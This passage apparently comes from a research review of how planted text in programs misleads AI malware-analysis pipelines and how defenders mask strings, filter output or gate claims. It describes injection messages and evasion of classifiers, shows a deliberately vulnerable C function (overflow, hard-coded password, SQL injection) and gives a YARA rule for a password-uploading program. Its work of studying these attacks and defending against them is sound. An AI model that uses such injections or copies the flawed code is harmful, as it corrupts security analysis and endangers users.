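A filter that searches for web addresses would miss one encoded in base64, but many language models can decode a short piece of base64. The defender would therefore have to mask the bytes before the server encodes them. This is harder than masking a string in decompiled code, because the agent chooses where to start and how much to read. A request may begin in the middle of a sentence or cover a mixture of text, numbers and machine code.

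An agent that receives placeholders may well try another tool. In two of Crawford and McClure's tests, the model found its analysis inconclusive and tried to request the decompiled function again.

The defender could remove the tool that reads raw bytes, but the agent may need it to examine encrypted data or tables of numbers. The defender could instead overwrite the strings in a copy of the program before any tool opens it. Every tool would then show the same placeholders, and the agent could not recover the original strings from the copy. But the defender would still need to decide which bytes are text, and the altered program might crash or behave differently if the agent ran it.

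According to Binary Ninja's manual, the list of tools may change as the server develops, so a filter that covers every output today could miss one after an update. A defender should repeat the test with planted phrases whenever the server changes.

*pyghidra-mcp* also lets an agent rename functions. If the agent bases a function's new name on a claim it read in a string, that claim could remain in the name after the defender masks all strings.

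### A pattern rule and a trained classifier

Crawford and McClure (May 2026) tested two filters that check a tool's output before it reaches the model. The attacks they used were like those in the earlier Naval Postgraduate School study, in which a string in a program made the agent describe a different program. Each attack included imitation chat markers and the decompiled code of the program that the agent was supposed to describe.

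The first filter is the pattern rule that looks for text between angle brackets. Crawford and McClure propose stopping the pipeline before it queries the model if the rule finds a match. They expect few false alarms because such pairs are uncommon in C. This is probably too optimistic for larger programs, since the ordinary C expression `i < list->length` contains both brackets. C++ also uses them in the names of common data types, and many programs contain pieces of HTML.

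The second filter is a neural classifier. Qwen3-1.7B, a small language model, converts each tool output into 2,048 numbers that represent its content. A separate network uses these numbers to estimate the probability that the output is malicious. The researchers trained only this separate network.

The training and test data came from simple C programs in online collections, most of them for beginners. The 100 harmless programs, once compiled, gave 275 tool outputs, and the 40 programs with attacks gave 89. The material was divided at random, with 70% for training, 15% for adjusting the design and 15% for the final test.

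Precision is the share of flagged outputs that are malicious, so false alarms lower it. Recall is the share of malicious outputs that the filter flags. The last column of the table is calculated from the published rates and doesn't appear in the paper.

| Filter | Precision | Recall | Accuracy | Counts that fit the rates (arithmetic) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pattern rule | 1.000 | 0.600 | 0.951 | 3 of 5 attacks flagged, 0 false alarms in 36 |
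| Neural classifier | 0.833 | 1.000 | 0.976 | 5 of 5 attacks flagged, 1 false alarm in 36 |

### The size of the test set

These rates are less precise than they look, because they probably describe only 41 tool outputs, five of them malicious. If there were five attacks, 41 is the only total that fits the published accuracy figures. A set of 82 with ten attacks would give the same rates, but that is more than the paper's description allows. Fifteen per cent of 364 outputs would be about 55, and no set of 55 gives these rates. The paper doesn't explain the difference.

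Five attacks are too few to measure recall. A classifier that caught only 55% of attacks in the long run would still catch five out of five about one time in 20. The pattern rule's three out of five is compatible with a true recall from about 15% to 95%. The test therefore can't establish that the classifier is nearly perfect, or even show with much confidence how far it outperforms the rule.

The false alarm rate is just as uncertain, and it matters more in a large program. One false alarm in 36 harmless outputs is about 3%. If that rate applied independently to every decompiled function, a harmless program with 37 functions would trigger at least one false alarm about 65% of the time. The malware sample that Cisco Talos gave to its models was that size, and commercial programs often have thousands of functions.

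The choice of programs may also have made the task easier. A beginner's exercise contains little text, so a long message about faulty decompiler results stands out. Real software contains more text, including help pages, error messages, licences and sometimes prompts for its own language model. If the researchers split the tool outputs at random rather than by program, the classifier may have been trained on one output of a program and tested on another from the same program.

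### Listings and decompiled functions

The researchers also tried the filters on 20 attacks they created with the genetic algorithm. Four of the programs had attacks in two functions, for a total of 24 functions. In a second version of each attack, they changed the punctuation of the imitation chat markers.

| Tool output | Flagged by the classifier, original markers | Flagged by the classifier, changed markers |
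|---|---|---|
| String listings | 20 of 20 | 20 of 20 |
| Decompiled functions | 15 of 24 | 17 of 24 |

The paper gives a precision of 1.000 for all four results, but this was guaranteed because every item contained an attack, so false alarms were impossible.

The pattern rule caught none of the attacks with changed punctuation, but the change made them less effective. The number that succeeded fell from 20 to 8 on Qwen3-8B and from 13 to 10 on the larger GPT-OSS-120B. A simple rule can therefore be worth having, because changing an attack to avoid it may weaken the attack.

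The classifier did worse on decompiled functions than on listings. Crawford and McClure don't investigate why, but a likely reason is that the attacks include imitation decompiler output, which stands out much less in real decompiler output than in a list of strings. The classifier also averages its numbers over the whole text, so a long function could dilute the signal from the attack.

A pipeline that checked both the listings and the decompiled functions would have caught all 20 original attacks through the listings. The classifier's weaker result on functions matters when the listing doesn't contain the attack, because the decompiled function is then the only place to catch it. The classifier flagged 15 functions, so it would have missed at least five of the 20 programs if it had checked only functions.

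When the researchers optimised the text against the classifier, it passed the filter and still misled the model for 20 of 20 programs with string listings and 13 of 20 with decompiler output. The paper also mentions two failures with string listings, which is hard to reconcile with 20 of 20. Either way, the classifier offered little protection against an attacker who could test messages on it. A longer search might have succeeded on the seven programs where the attack through decompiler output failed, so those failures aren't evidence that the programs were safe.

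An attacker without access to the classifier would have more difficulty, so keeping a filter private has some value. The paper doesn't test how well text optimised against one classifier works against another.

Protection also depends on what the pipeline does after an alarm. Crawford and McClure suggest leaving malicious tool output out of the prompt, but if that output is a decompiled function, the model loses the function's code along with the attacker's message. An attacker could then hide harmful code from the model by placing recognisable injected text beside it. Stopping the analysis altogether has the same weakness as a refusal if nobody follows up. It is safer to treat the file as suspicious and send it to a person or a conventional scanner, because few legitimate programs contain messages that imitate an analysis tool.

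Santos-Grueiro tested redaction together with stronger instructions, a more structured presentation and a check on the answer, using 30 programs and four models. The redaction was a filter that removed only text resembling a prompt. The models accepted the planted claim or instruction in 38 of 480 cases (7.9%) with ordinary prompts and in 28 (5.8%) with all four changes. The check changed none of those 28 results. The small improvement gives no reason to think that redaction alone would solve the problem.

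### Masking doesn't have to recognise an attack

Crawford and McClure's results are evidence about filtering, not about blanket masking, which better wording can't defeat. The researchers didn't run the same attacks with every string masked, so neither the 13 successes against the classifier nor the 20 detections in string listings shows whether masking would work.

Masking can still fail if the defender doesn't find all the text. For example, if a pipeline replaces only the strings in the string listing, any string missing from the listing would stay in the decompiled code. A better method is to have the decompiler mark every string literal it prints, then replace the marked literals. This would cover text that the listing missed, but not names, section labels or logs.

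With either method, the defender must also decide whether to mask numbers, because a decompiler can display a few characters of text as a single number, as it did with the word "file" in macOS.Gaslight. Masking every number would remove the sizes, addresses and error codes that a model needs to follow almost any program. A few characters are hardly enough for an instruction, so a defender could reasonably mask only long blocks of data and leave ordinary numbers alone.

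### Is injected text always detectable?

Cisco Talos is more optimistic about detection. Fetterman writes that text intended to influence AI analysis "must always be plaintext and therefore is always detectable". This makes two separate claims, that attackers must store their text as plaintext and that defenders can always recognise it.

Known malware mostly supports the claim about storage. Skynet's author encrypted the Tor program inside the malware but left the message to language models readable, and Check Point Research found that message as an ordinary C++ string. Leaving it readable made sense because a model that received only the file's strings couldn't have read an encrypted message.

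Injected text has to be readable only when it reaches the model, so a program can store it in compressed or encrypted form and reveal it when it runs. The message would then appear in a sandbox log but not in a string listing of the original file. Some agents also use unpackers, which recover the contents of compressed or encrypted programs, as ESET notes in ITmedia's *マルウェアに「核兵器の作り方を教えて」 AIによるコード解析を止めさせる新手口「GuardBreaker」*. The more of these tools a pipeline uses, the less an attacker needs to leave the message readable in the file.

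The claim about detection is weaker, because text can be readable without being recognisable as an attack. The nine functions that Crawford and McClure's classifier missed all contained readable messages. The character sequences that Sun, Oprea and Wong used against vulnerability detectors didn't need to make sense to a person.

False evidence is harder still to recognise. Santos-Grueiro gives `credential_dump_enabled` as an example of a misleading string, but a real password stealer could have a setting with that name. A filter that reads only the string cannot determine whether it is false. An analyst would have to check whether the program contains code that steals passwords, which is what the model was supposed to find out.

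Talos's collection of 84 samples can't settle the question, because it includes only samples that at least one method could detect.

The operator of a pipeline can record everything sent to the model, including all tool output, and search that record when researchers report a new attack. This would identify files that need another look, but only after the model had given its verdict. Fetterman's main recommendation is that developers build pipelines that treat text in a sample as evidence and never as an instruction, an approach that doesn't depend on detection.

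## What does the analysis lose without strings?

Without strings, a model can usually still follow a program's steps, but it often can't tell what they are for. The server that a program contacts, the files it opens and the demands it shows a victim all appear in its strings, and so do some security flaws. No one appears to have published a measurement of how many more malicious programs a model misses when a defender masks every string. If one malicious program in ten contained injected text, and the text worked as well as Cloudflare's averages suggest, stripping would be worthwhile only if it reduced the detection rate by less than 1.4 percentage points.

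### Evidence of purpose

Malicious and legitimate programs often call the same functions. A legitimate Windows program may save its window size in the registry, the database where Windows keeps settings. Malware that starts whenever the user logs in often does so by writing to the registry too. Both may call `RegSetValueExW`, and only the strings show which setting they change.

| String | What an analyst can learn from it | What remains after masking |
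|---|---|---|
| Server address | Where the program sends data or gets its orders | A call that opens a connection |
| File path | Which files it reads, such as a browser's saved passwords | A call that opens a file |
| Registry key | Whether it changes a preference or arranges to start at login | A call that writes to the registry |
| Command | What it asks the operating system to do, such as delete backups | A call that runs a command |
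| Ransom note | That it encrypts files to demand money, unlike a backup tool | A call that writes or displays text |
| Error message | What the programmer expected a function to do | A call that prints text |

Typed placeholders preserve part of this evidence. The placeholder `[WEB ADDRESS, 26]` shows a model that the program contains an address, but not whether the address belongs to the developer or to an attacker.

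The last column of the table also depends on the model being able to read the names of system functions. Some malware looks these functions up by name while it runs, which keeps them out of the program's list of imports. The function's name is then a string, so masking it also hides the call.

Strings also help an analyst find the important part of a program. *Extending LLVM for Code Obfuscation (2 of 2)*, a guide from the security company Praetorian, gives the example of a user agent, the text a program uses to identify itself to a web server. An analyst who finds one in a malware sample can follow the references to it and reach the code that communicates with the attacker. An AI agent can do the same through Ghidra. Without the string, it would have to start from something else, such as calls to networking functions, or read more of the program, which takes a lot of work when the program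 is large.

### Flaws inside a string

In vulnerability review, the mistake may be in the string itself. The following invented C function reads a name and a staff code from a line of text, then looks up the person's biography in an SQLite database.

```c
void handle_request(sqlite3 *db, const char *line)
{
    char name[16], code[16];
    sscanf(line, "%s %s", name, code);
    if (strcmp(code, "harbour42") == 0)
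        open_admin_menu();
    char *query = sqlite3_mprintf("SELECT bio FROM users WHERE name = '%s'", name);
    sqlite3_exec(db, query, show_bio, NULL, NULL);
}
```

The program has three flaws. The first string sets no limit on the length of the name or the code, so a long one overflows its 16-byte space. The second is a hard-coded password, which anyone can read in the compiled program and use to open the administrator's menu. The third allows SQL injection, because a name that contains an apostrophe can alter the database command.

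With every literal masked, the function becomes:

```c
void handle_request(sqlite3 *db, const char *line)
{
    char name[16], code[16];
    sscanf(line, "[STRING]", name, code);
    if (strcmp(code, "[STRING]") == 0)
        open_admin_menu();
    char *query = sqlite3_mprintf("[STRING]", name);
    sqlite3_exec(db, query, show_bio, NULL, NULL);
}
```

A careful programmer would have written `%15s` in the first string, which limits the length, and `%q` in the third, which makes SQLite treat apostrophes as ordinary text. Masking makes the careful and flawed versions identical in both places. A typed placeholder that includes the length would give a small clue to the first flaw, because `%15s` is longer than `%s`, but none to the SQL injection, because `%q` and `%s` have the same length.

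The hard-coded password is easier to find, because the model can still detect that some fixed text opens the administrator's menu, even with the text itself removed. But in a stripped binary, the name `open_admin_menu` would be missing too, and the password check would look like a check for an ordinary command such as "help".

Masking does not hide the best-known kind of format-string flaw. In `printf(name)`, the program uses text from the user as the format string, so a user who types format codes can make it read or change memory. The flaw is recognisable because the call has no literal format string, so there is nothing to mask. Similarly, a model can still recognise some SQL injection when the program joins text with a plus sign, as in `run_query("[STRING]" + name)`.

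A defender could reduce the loss by keeping the format codes and masking the words around them, as in `"[TEXT]%s[TEXT]"`. These codes follow strict rules, so an attacker has almost no room to write a sentence in them. In the example, this would preserve the evidence for two of the three flaws, though not for the password.

### Identifying malware families

A malware family is a group of malicious programs that share code or behaviour. Knowing the family helps an analyst predict what a new sample will do. *Rethinking and Exploring String-Based Malware Family Classification in the Era of LLMs* measured how well strings alone can identify a sample's family, using 4,347 samples from 67 families.

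The researchers extracted strings with FLOSS, a tool that finds readable text and recovers some text that a program hides or assembles while it runs. They discarded strings that occurred in more than one family or were shorter than 13 characters, then kept up to 10,000 of the most common remaining strings per family. This reduced the average number of strings per family from about 377,000 to about 7,000.

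To classify a new sample, the system picks up to 1,000 of its strings and finds the ten most similar strings in the database for each. It scores every match as

$$\text{score} = \frac{F}{N} \times \text{similarity}$$

where *F* is how often the matching string occurs in its family and *N* is the number of samples from that family in the database. It then combines the 100 best scores by family and chooses the family with the highest total. A string that resembles one found in nearly every sample of a family therefore counts for more than one that resembles a rarity.

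The researchers built the database from samples found before 2023 and tested it on 327 samples from around January 2024. The first guess was correct for 40% of them, and the correct family was among the first three guesses for 47%. Random guessing among 67 families would be correct about 1.5% of the time. When the researchers instead gave the best matches to a fine-tuned GPT-4o mini, it was correct for 37%, about ten samples fewer, so the difference could be chance.

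Accuracy varied widely between families. The system identified every test sample from 13 families and none from 19 others, though each family had at most five. One reason for the failures is that only 31% of the extracted strings were meaningful, while the rest were encoded or looked random. For five families with poor results, the researchers added strings that appeared while the malware ran in a sandbox, and average accuracy rose from 20% to 44%. This increase is based on about 25 samples, and the initial accuracy figures for three of the five families differ from those in the main results.

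These results show that strings contain a lot of information about some malware, but they don't show how much a model would lose without them. A model that also has the code might recognise the same family from its functions. The earlier research that the paper reviews is mixed. A 2001 system that relied on strings and other static features did better than the antivirus signatures of its time, but in a large 2023 comparison, strings added little to other information about a file.

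### Tests that removed something else

To measure how much the analysis loses without strings, researchers would need to mask the string literals, leave everything else unchanged and compare the results. This kind of experiment, which removes one part of the input, is called an ablation. There appears to be no published ablation of strings for a language model that names functions, summarises code or detects malware. The closest experiments removed other things.

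*MASCOT-Android* (Li, S and colleagues, 2026) tested malware detection on the source code of 606 malicious and 606 harmless Android apps. The researchers removed comments, replaced names with neutral ones such as `variable1`, and removed import statements, which list the libraries a program uses.

| Source code given to the detector | Accuracy |
|---|---|
| Original | 89.8% |
| No imports | 88.9% |
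| No imports or comments | 88.9% |
| No imports, comments or original names | 89.5% |
| Imports kept, but no comments or original names | 90.6% |

The results are all within two percentage points, or about 20 apps, of each other. Comments and names seem to have contributed almost nothing to the verdict. This is mildly encouraging for stripping, because it suggests a detector can lose a lot of readable text and still work. However, the detector was a simple classifier that counted short sequences of characters. It couldn't use the meaning of a name as a language model can, so it lost less when names were removed. Li and colleagues also left the string literals in place. Fragments of words such as "trojan" and "phishing" were among the strongest signs of malware, and some of them may have come from strings.

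*MalCVE* (2025), by contrast, offers some evidence that strings help the analysis. It describes a system that uses language models to detect malware and match it with known vulnerabilities. Accuracy fell by 8% when the system skipped deobfuscation, which undoes attempts to disguise code. The researchers attribute the fall to the model's difficulty in identifying libraries and methods. In one case, the deobfuscator had recovered hidden strings that revealed a call to `findClass`, which finds part of a program by its name. Masking strings could hide the same kind of evidence. But deobfuscation can change much more than the strings, so the 8% fall isn't an estimate of the effect of stripping them.

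*MalTotal* (2026) measures the effect of removing code. It looks for malicious code in software repositories, using a "slicer" to select the relevant parts of a file for the model. When the slicer kept only the lines strictly needed for execution, the F1 score (a combined measure of precision and recall) fell to 86.5%. A version that kept whole functions scored 91.1%, with about twice as much text. Giving the model entire files substantially reduced recall. The slicer normally traces sensitive variables back to their origins, and switching this off also reduced recall. Such a trace may end at a string literal, such as the address a program sends a password to, so masking literals could remove the last and most informative step.

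None of these experiments involved injected text. Santos-Grueiro tested redaction under attack, but only together with other changes. A direct test would give a model the same malicious programs with and without strings, and test each version with and without an attacker's message. It would also need harmless programs, because a model that lacks evidence might label everything malicious.

### Missing and misleading strings

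For some malware, the loss would be small because the strings are already unreadable. Malware authors commonly encrypt strings to slow down analysts and to avoid detection by tools that search for known text. Praetorian built a demonstration tool that encrypts a program's string literals during compilation and adds code to decrypt each one when the program needs it, so none of the literals appears in a string listing.

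An attacker can encrypt the incriminating strings and leave only a message to language models readable. Skynet's author did something similar by encrypting the Tor program but not the message. Stripping strings from such a file removes the attack and almost no useful evidence. Much more evidence is lost when the malware's author hid nothing.

Encrypted strings can still be useful to an agent. Quarkslab gave Claude Code a program with six strings, each encrypted with AES-256, a standard cipher. The agent usually found the code that decrypted the strings, copied it into a Python script and ran it. Recovering strings from protected programs took about 45 minutes on average, though some of the agent's reports described work it hadn't done. A defender who wants to mask every string would have to withhold the decrypted ones too, so the analysis would lose what the agent had recovered.

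Text can also mislead a model when nobody intended it to. In one of Quarkslab's tests, a filename contained "sh2", which meant "string hider, version 2". The agent took it for the SH-2, a processor from the 1990s, and spent time looking for a tool to decode its instructions. Quarkslab concluded that a suggestive filename or an alarming constant can steer a whole analysis. Masking could prevent some of these mistakes, and a model might do better without certain strings.

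Masking could also lead a model to raise more false alarms, because it removes text that explains what harmless programs do. Quarkslab's agents described one harmless program as characteristic of spyware or of malware that receives commands from a server. The program had protective checks that read files, tested permissions and raised signals, which can look malicious out of context. Legitimate software often includes help pages, licences and a company name that explain such behaviour, although this text is weak evidence because an attacker can copy it.

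### YARA and capa

Conventional tools can use strings without passing them to a model. YARA is a widely used tool that searches files for patterns that an analyst has described in rules. This rule would match the password-stealing function from the earlier comparison of stripping methods:

```
rule example_uploader
{
    strings:
        $address = "https://example.com/upload"
        $path = "/home/user/passwords.txt"
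    condition:
        all of them
}
```

A YARA rule can also look for byte sequences or file properties, but ordinary text is one of the easiest patterns to write and check. The open-source tool capa, from the security company Mandiant, uses higher-level rules that describe capabilities, such as encrypting data or starting at login, as combinations of system calls, numbers, strings and other features. A rule for starting at login can require both a call that writes to the registry and the name of the relevant registry key.

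Neither tool interprets sentences as instructions, so neither will follow an injected message. If a pipeline runs them on the original file, they can still use all the strings that a defender later masks for the model. The pipeline can then give the model the names of the rules that matched. The defender wrote those names, so an attacker can influence which ones appear but not what they contain. Both tools can also print the matched text, which the pipeline must not pass to the model.

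Chawla and Prasad invite the model itself to apply "YARA rules" to the decompiled code. If a defender masked the strings before giving the model the code, the model couldn't apply any rule that depends on them.

Rules recover only part of the loss, because they match only what somebody has already described. A new server address or an unusual ransom note may match no rule, whereas a model might interpret it correctly. An attacker can also add strings that trigger rules for the wrong malware family, just as they can mislead a model with false evidence.

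### Injected text as an indicator

A message that tells an AI reviewer to report no malware is good evidence that the author expected such a review and wanted to influence it. Few honest programmers have a reason to write one. Stripping removes this evidence along with the attack, so a model may describe the script as ordinary.

Some models already use the text as evidence. In Cloudflare's test, some became more suspicious of scripts with 1,000 comments, and one flagged comments in Russian as "social engineering indicators". Removing the text from what these models see would help the attacker.

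Prompt-like text in software isn't proof of malice. Cloudflare warns against classifying legitimate AI-related applications as malicious because of overzealous documentation or instructions. A chatbot may contain prompts for its own model, and a security researcher's test file may contain a copy of a known attack. Suspicion should depend on the text's intended reader and the request it contains. A request to ignore malicious code is much more suspicious than a request to answer customers politely.

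To keep the evidence, another component has to check the original text before the pipeline masks it. It could record the injected message's wording and location for a human analyst, and raise the file's risk score without showing the text to the model. A classifier like Crawford and McClure's could look for these messages, but attackers can learn to evade it, so a file that triggers no alert may still contain an injected message.

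Keeping the record separate from the model's answer also avoids cutting the analysis short. If the pipeline told the model that a file contained an attempted injection, the model might classify the file as malicious for that reason alone and stop analysing what it does. An analyst who needs to know which passwords a program steals would then have a correct verdict but little information about the program's behaviour.

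### How much loss is acceptable?

Whether stripping reduces the number of missed malware samples depends on four quantities:

- *m*<sub>0</sub> is the miss rate for malware without injected text, when the model can read the strings
- *m*<sub>1</sub> is the miss rate for malware with injected text, when the model can read the strings
- *q* is the share of malicious samples that contain injected text
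- *s* is the miss rate after stripping.

Without stripping, the overall miss rate is the average of *m*<sub>0</sub> and *m*<sub>1</sub>, weighted by how common each kind of sample is:

$$(1-q)\,m_0 + q\,m_1 = m_0 + q\,(m_1 - m_0)$$

Suppose that stripping neutralises the injected text completely. The miss rate is then *s* for all samples, and stripping reduces misses only if *s* is smaller than the expression above. Subtracting *m*<sub>0</sub> from both sides gives the break-even condition:

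$$s - m_0 < q\,(m_1 - m_0)$$

The left side is the loss from stripping, which is the extra malware the model misses because it has less evidence. The right side is the benefit, which comes only from samples with injected text, whereas the loss applies to every sample.

Cloudflare's averages are *m*<sub>0</sub> = 32.7% for scripts without added comments and *m*<sub>1</sub> = 46.7% for scripts in which comments made up less than 1% of the file, a difference of 14 percentage points. If 1% of malicious samples contained injected text, stripping could therefore lose at most 0.14 points.

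These figures concern comments rather than strings, and file size may explain most or all of the 14 points. Weighting Cloudflare's results by the number of scripts in each size group compares the same scripts before and after. With that weighting, one added comment lowered detection by about 1.7 points, and 20 comments didn't lower it at all. The effect varied by model, and detection by the most affected one fell 23 points with 20 comments.

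The table shows the largest acceptable loss, in percentage points, under several assumptions. The last column assumes an attack that always succeeds against a model that would otherwise miss 32.7% of malware.

| Share of malware with injected text | Cloudflare's averages | Weighted by file size, one comment | Most affected model, 20 comments | Attack that always succeeds |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 0.14 | 0.02 | 0.23 | 0.67 |
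| 10% | 1.4 | 0.17 | 2.3 | 6.7 |
| 100% | 14 | 1.7 | 23 | 67 |

If few attackers inject text, preventing injection doesn't justify a large loss of detection, even if every attack would succeed. When 1% of malware contains injected text, a defender who loses a full percentage point of detection by stripping strings will always miss more malware overall than one who keeps them, because *m*<sub>1</sub> in the formula can't exceed 100%.

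An attack can do more damage to a better detector. In Chawla and Prasad's test, for example, fine-tuning cut the miss rate from 41% to 16%. An attack could raise that rate by at most 59 points before fine-tuning, but by up to 84 points after it. Stripping could therefore become more worthwhile as models improve, provided they don't also become harder to fool or more dependent on strings.

The same condition can be used to calculate how common injected text would have to be for stripping to help. If stripping lowered the detection rate by five percentage points, it would reduce misses only when more than 36% of malware contained text as effective as Cloudflare's averages suggest. If the attack always succeeded, the threshold would be about 7%.

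Nobody knows the real value of *q*, and it can't be estimated from Talos's samples because the search for them was targeted. Attackers can easily raise *q* by copying a message, as several did with FRUITSHELL's comment. If an effective message became public, a defender who had decided against stripping might have to reconsider within weeks. Widespread stripping could lower *q*, because attackers would have less reason to add text that no model receives.

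The condition assumes that stripping works perfectly. If an attacker's words remain in function names or logs and keep half their effect, the acceptable loss is halved. The formula also leaves out false alarms. A defender who misses slightly less malware but blocks many more harmless programs may be worse off.

A defender can decide file by file whether to strip strings. Suppose that 10% of malicious samples contain injected text, and that a filter flags 80% of those and 3% of the other malicious samples. About 75% of the flagged malware would contain injected text, so stripping could lose up to 10.5 points there and still reduce misses, on Cloudflare's averages. Only about 2% of the unflagged malware would contain it, and the acceptable loss would be 0.3 points. Stripping strings only from flagged files would therefore make more sense than treating all files alike, unless attackers learn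 to avoid the filter.

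## Which defences keep the text and limit its influence?

A pipeline can let the model read everything in a program and still limit the effect of injected text by having ordinary software decide which actions the model may take and which of its claims count as proven. Santos-Grueiro tested such a system, and its checks blocked every planted action and false claim in the main experiments. The checks protect less well against a false description that leads the model to the wrong verdict, because software can refuse a forbidden action more easily than it can detect a wrong conclusion.

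### Text obeyed, believed or saved

Santos-Grueiro calls the attacks he studies "representation-confusion attacks in reverse engineering", or RARE. The analysis tools report the program's text correctly, but the pipeline then gives that text a role it shouldn't have. He measures three failures:

- Authority confusion means that the model obeys text from the program as if the analyst had written it. For example, a note in the program says to skip the network checks, and the agent skips them.
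- Evidence confusion means that the pipeline accepts the text as proof. A string mentions password theft, and the report lists password theft as confirmed.
- Tainted-state promotion means that the pipeline stores an unproven claim as an established finding, which a later session then relies on.

The same text is harmless if the pipeline treats it only as an observation. For example, a report can quote the note about network checks or list password theft as a possibility to investigate.

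RARE-Bench is a set of small, harmless C test programs compiled for Linux. Each program has a clean version, a control version with extra harmless content and a version with planted text. All three behave the same way on a fixed set of inputs, so if a model proposes something only when the planted text is present, the program's behaviour can't be the reason. Another version contains proper evidence for a true claim, to check whether a defence also blocks correct findings.

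The RARE-Guard defence runs four checks outside the model. Tool Authorization decides which tool calls may run. Support Gate checks whether the evidence for a claim is of the right kind, and Provenance Gate counts evidence from one origin only once. State Gate preserves the status of saved findings. The table gives the main results for GPT-5.5 and DeepSeek-V3.2, which each analysed 20 programs (16 in the last row).

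| Defence | Outcome counted | Without the defence | With the defence | Legitimate cases allowed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Text presented only as data | Unsafe actions proposed | 35 of 40 | 15 of 40 | Not measured |
| Tool Authorization | Unsafe actions approved | 15 of 40 | 0 of 40 | 40 of 40 |
| Provenance Gate, one origin | False claims validated | 23 of 40 | 0 of 40 | 40 of 40 |
| Provenance Gate, three tools combined | False claims validated | 32 of 32 | 0 of 32 | 32 of 32 |

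### Presenting program text as data

The ordinary prompt mixed the program's text with the rest of the input. The data-only prompt put that text in records labelled as data and kept the analyst's instructions separate. This separation prevented more than half of the unsafe proposals, but not all, which fits Ye and colleagues' finding that role markers have a limited effect.

In Santos-Grueiro's larger experiment, with 11,520 calls, combining redaction with three other changes reduced the share of cases in which the models accepted the planted claim or instruction only from 7.9% to 5.8%. Task success on programs with planted text also fell, from 86.2% to 84.5%.

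Stronger instructions, one of the other changes, gave a task success rate of 87.2% on their own, so the full combination wasn't clearly better than the simplest change. The full combination lowered success on clean programs from 91.9% to 90.4%, which suggests it slightly reduces performance even without an attack. Santos-Grueiro calls these results exploratory because he decided exactly which responses to count as failures after collecting them.

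### Permission to use tools

With Tool Authorization, the model submits a request to use a tool instead of running it directly. The request has a fixed format and names the tool, its arguments, the purpose and the records that prompted the request. An ordinary program checks it against a list of approved tools, limits on arguments and resources, and the permissions the analyst has given. The program rejects, for example, requests for an unrestricted command line or for a connection to a network address that the attacker chose. Text from the analysed software can still influence which permitted tool the model requests, but it can't add a permission.

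The software denied all 15 unsafe proposals that remained after the text had been labelled as data. When the analyst made the matching request, the software approved it in all 40 cases, so it wasn't blocking every action of that kind. However, only eight of those 40 cases ended in a successful task, a problem that a defender who counted only blocked attacks would overlook. Santos-Grueiro concludes that correct authorisation doesn't guarantee a successful analysis, but doesn't explain why the other 32 cases failed.

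In a separate test in which the models could use tools over two turns, neither model acted on the planted text, so Tool Authorization had nothing to deny. The test therefore doesn't show whether this defence would have stopped an attack under those conditions. When the analyst requested the same action, the software ran it in all 32 sessions, but only six ended with a correct report, compared with 31 when the planted text was present and the analyst made no such request.

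Tool Authorization also can't help when injected text persuades an agent to do less. The false error messages in macOS.Gaslight seem intended to make an agent give up, and an agent that gives up makes no request for the software to deny. A pipeline could require certain steps, such as listing the imported functions and decompiling the main function, and treat the analysis as incomplete until the agent has done them all. RARE-Guard doesn't do this, and the idea is untested.

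### Counting origins instead of records

RARE-Guard uses two stages to stop a pipeline from counting one piece of text as several findings.

Support Gate checks whether each record can support the type of claim the model is making. A string proves only that the text is present. A claim that the program has some capability may require reachable code, and a claim about what the program did may require an event recorded when it ran. If the evidence is insufficient, Support Gate downgrades the claim instead of deleting it.

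Let *Q* be the set of records that pass this check, and let *k* be the number of pieces of evidence that the claim requires. In simplified form, Support Gate validates the claim if

$$|Q| \geq k$$

Provenance Gate replaces the number of records with the number of different origins. If *o*(*x*) is the origin of record *x*, the condition becomes

$$|\{o(x) : x \in Q\}| \geq k$$

Suppose a claim requires two pieces of evidence, and Ghidra, r2pipe and angr all report the same item from the program. Support Gate validates the claim because it counts three records, but Provenance Gate does not, because it counts only their one shared origin.

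Santos-Grueiro applied both rules to the same draft reports, so differences in the models' wording can't explain the results. When he gave each record a different false origin, the two rules agreed in all 384 comparisons. The improvement therefore came from knowing where the evidence originated.

When the output of three tools was combined, half of the 32 false claims each rested on records of a single location in the program. The other 16 rested on different locations whose contents came from a common source. A rule that only merged records of the same location still validated all 16. Provenance Gate rejected them with a further rule that traced the records back to their source. A pipeline therefore has to save where each record came from as it extracts the evidence, because it can't reliably work this out later from plain text.

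The zeros in the table follow almost automatically from the rules, because Provenance Gate must reject a claim that requires two origins and has only one. The more informative results are that the true claims survived and that the pipeline could track origins through three real analysis tools. The method depends on that tracking. If an attacker planted the same false evidence in several places with no recorded connection, Provenance Gate would count each place as a separate origin. Santos-Grueiro acknowledges that different recorded origins aren't necessarily independent.

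Provenance Gate leaves other mistakes uncorrected. In the test with combined tools, Support Gate validated a false claim in six of 32 cases with clean programs and four of 32 with control programs, and Provenance Gate changed none of these decisions. Across 320 responses in the earlier test, the share that both completed the task and made the right security decision rose from 40.6% to 47.8%, so more than half still failed in at least one respect.

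### Final reports and saved notes

A correct decision about a claim doesn't help if the model can repeat the claim elsewhere. In all 32 false cases with combined tools, the model's free-text answer stated the false claim even though Provenance Gate had downgraded it. Santos-Grueiro solved this by having an ordinary program write the final report from the checked claims alone. All 864 reports then matched the decisions. But the analyst no longer receives explanations or doubts that don't fit the form for a claim.

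State Gate stores each finding with its status, its supporting evidence and a warning that it came from an untrusted program. Retrieving a hypothesis doesn't change its status to fact. This part of RARE-Guard is largely untested, because neither model tried to upgrade a saved hypothesis without new evidence. When new evidence was available, the pipeline validated 11 of 16 hypotheses saved with their labels and 8 of 16 saved as plain text, a difference that could easily be due to chance.

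### How far the results apply

All the programs were synthetic and harmless, and ran on one type of computer. The main tests used only two models and short, restricted tasks, whereas malware analysis may involve encrypted code, thousands of functions and days of investigation. The results show that the checks can work, but not how often they would fail when used by a working security team.

Santos-Grueiro also finalised the programs and planted text before running the main tests, so no attacker could study RARE-Guard and revise the text. This probably matters less for the test of Tool Authorization than for the test of data-only presentation, because better wording might persuade the model to make an unsafe request but can't change the list of permitted tools. An attacker could still look for mistakes in that list, or for a harmful use of a permitted tool.

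### Models trained to resist injection

Developers can also train models to ignore injected instructions. Crawford and McClure write that this is difficult because the model must follow instructions and detect unauthorised ones at the same time, so developers often put defences outside the model.

*A Critical Evaluation of Defenses against Prompt Injection Attacks* (Jia, Shao and colleagues, 2025) tested two training methods on the small open-weight model Llama-3-8B-Instruct. StruQ marks instructions and data separately and trains the model to follow only the text marked as instructions. SecAlign trains the model on examples of desirable and undesirable responses to injected text. The methods' developers had reported that both worked well, but most of their tests used a single injected request to print a fixed phrase.

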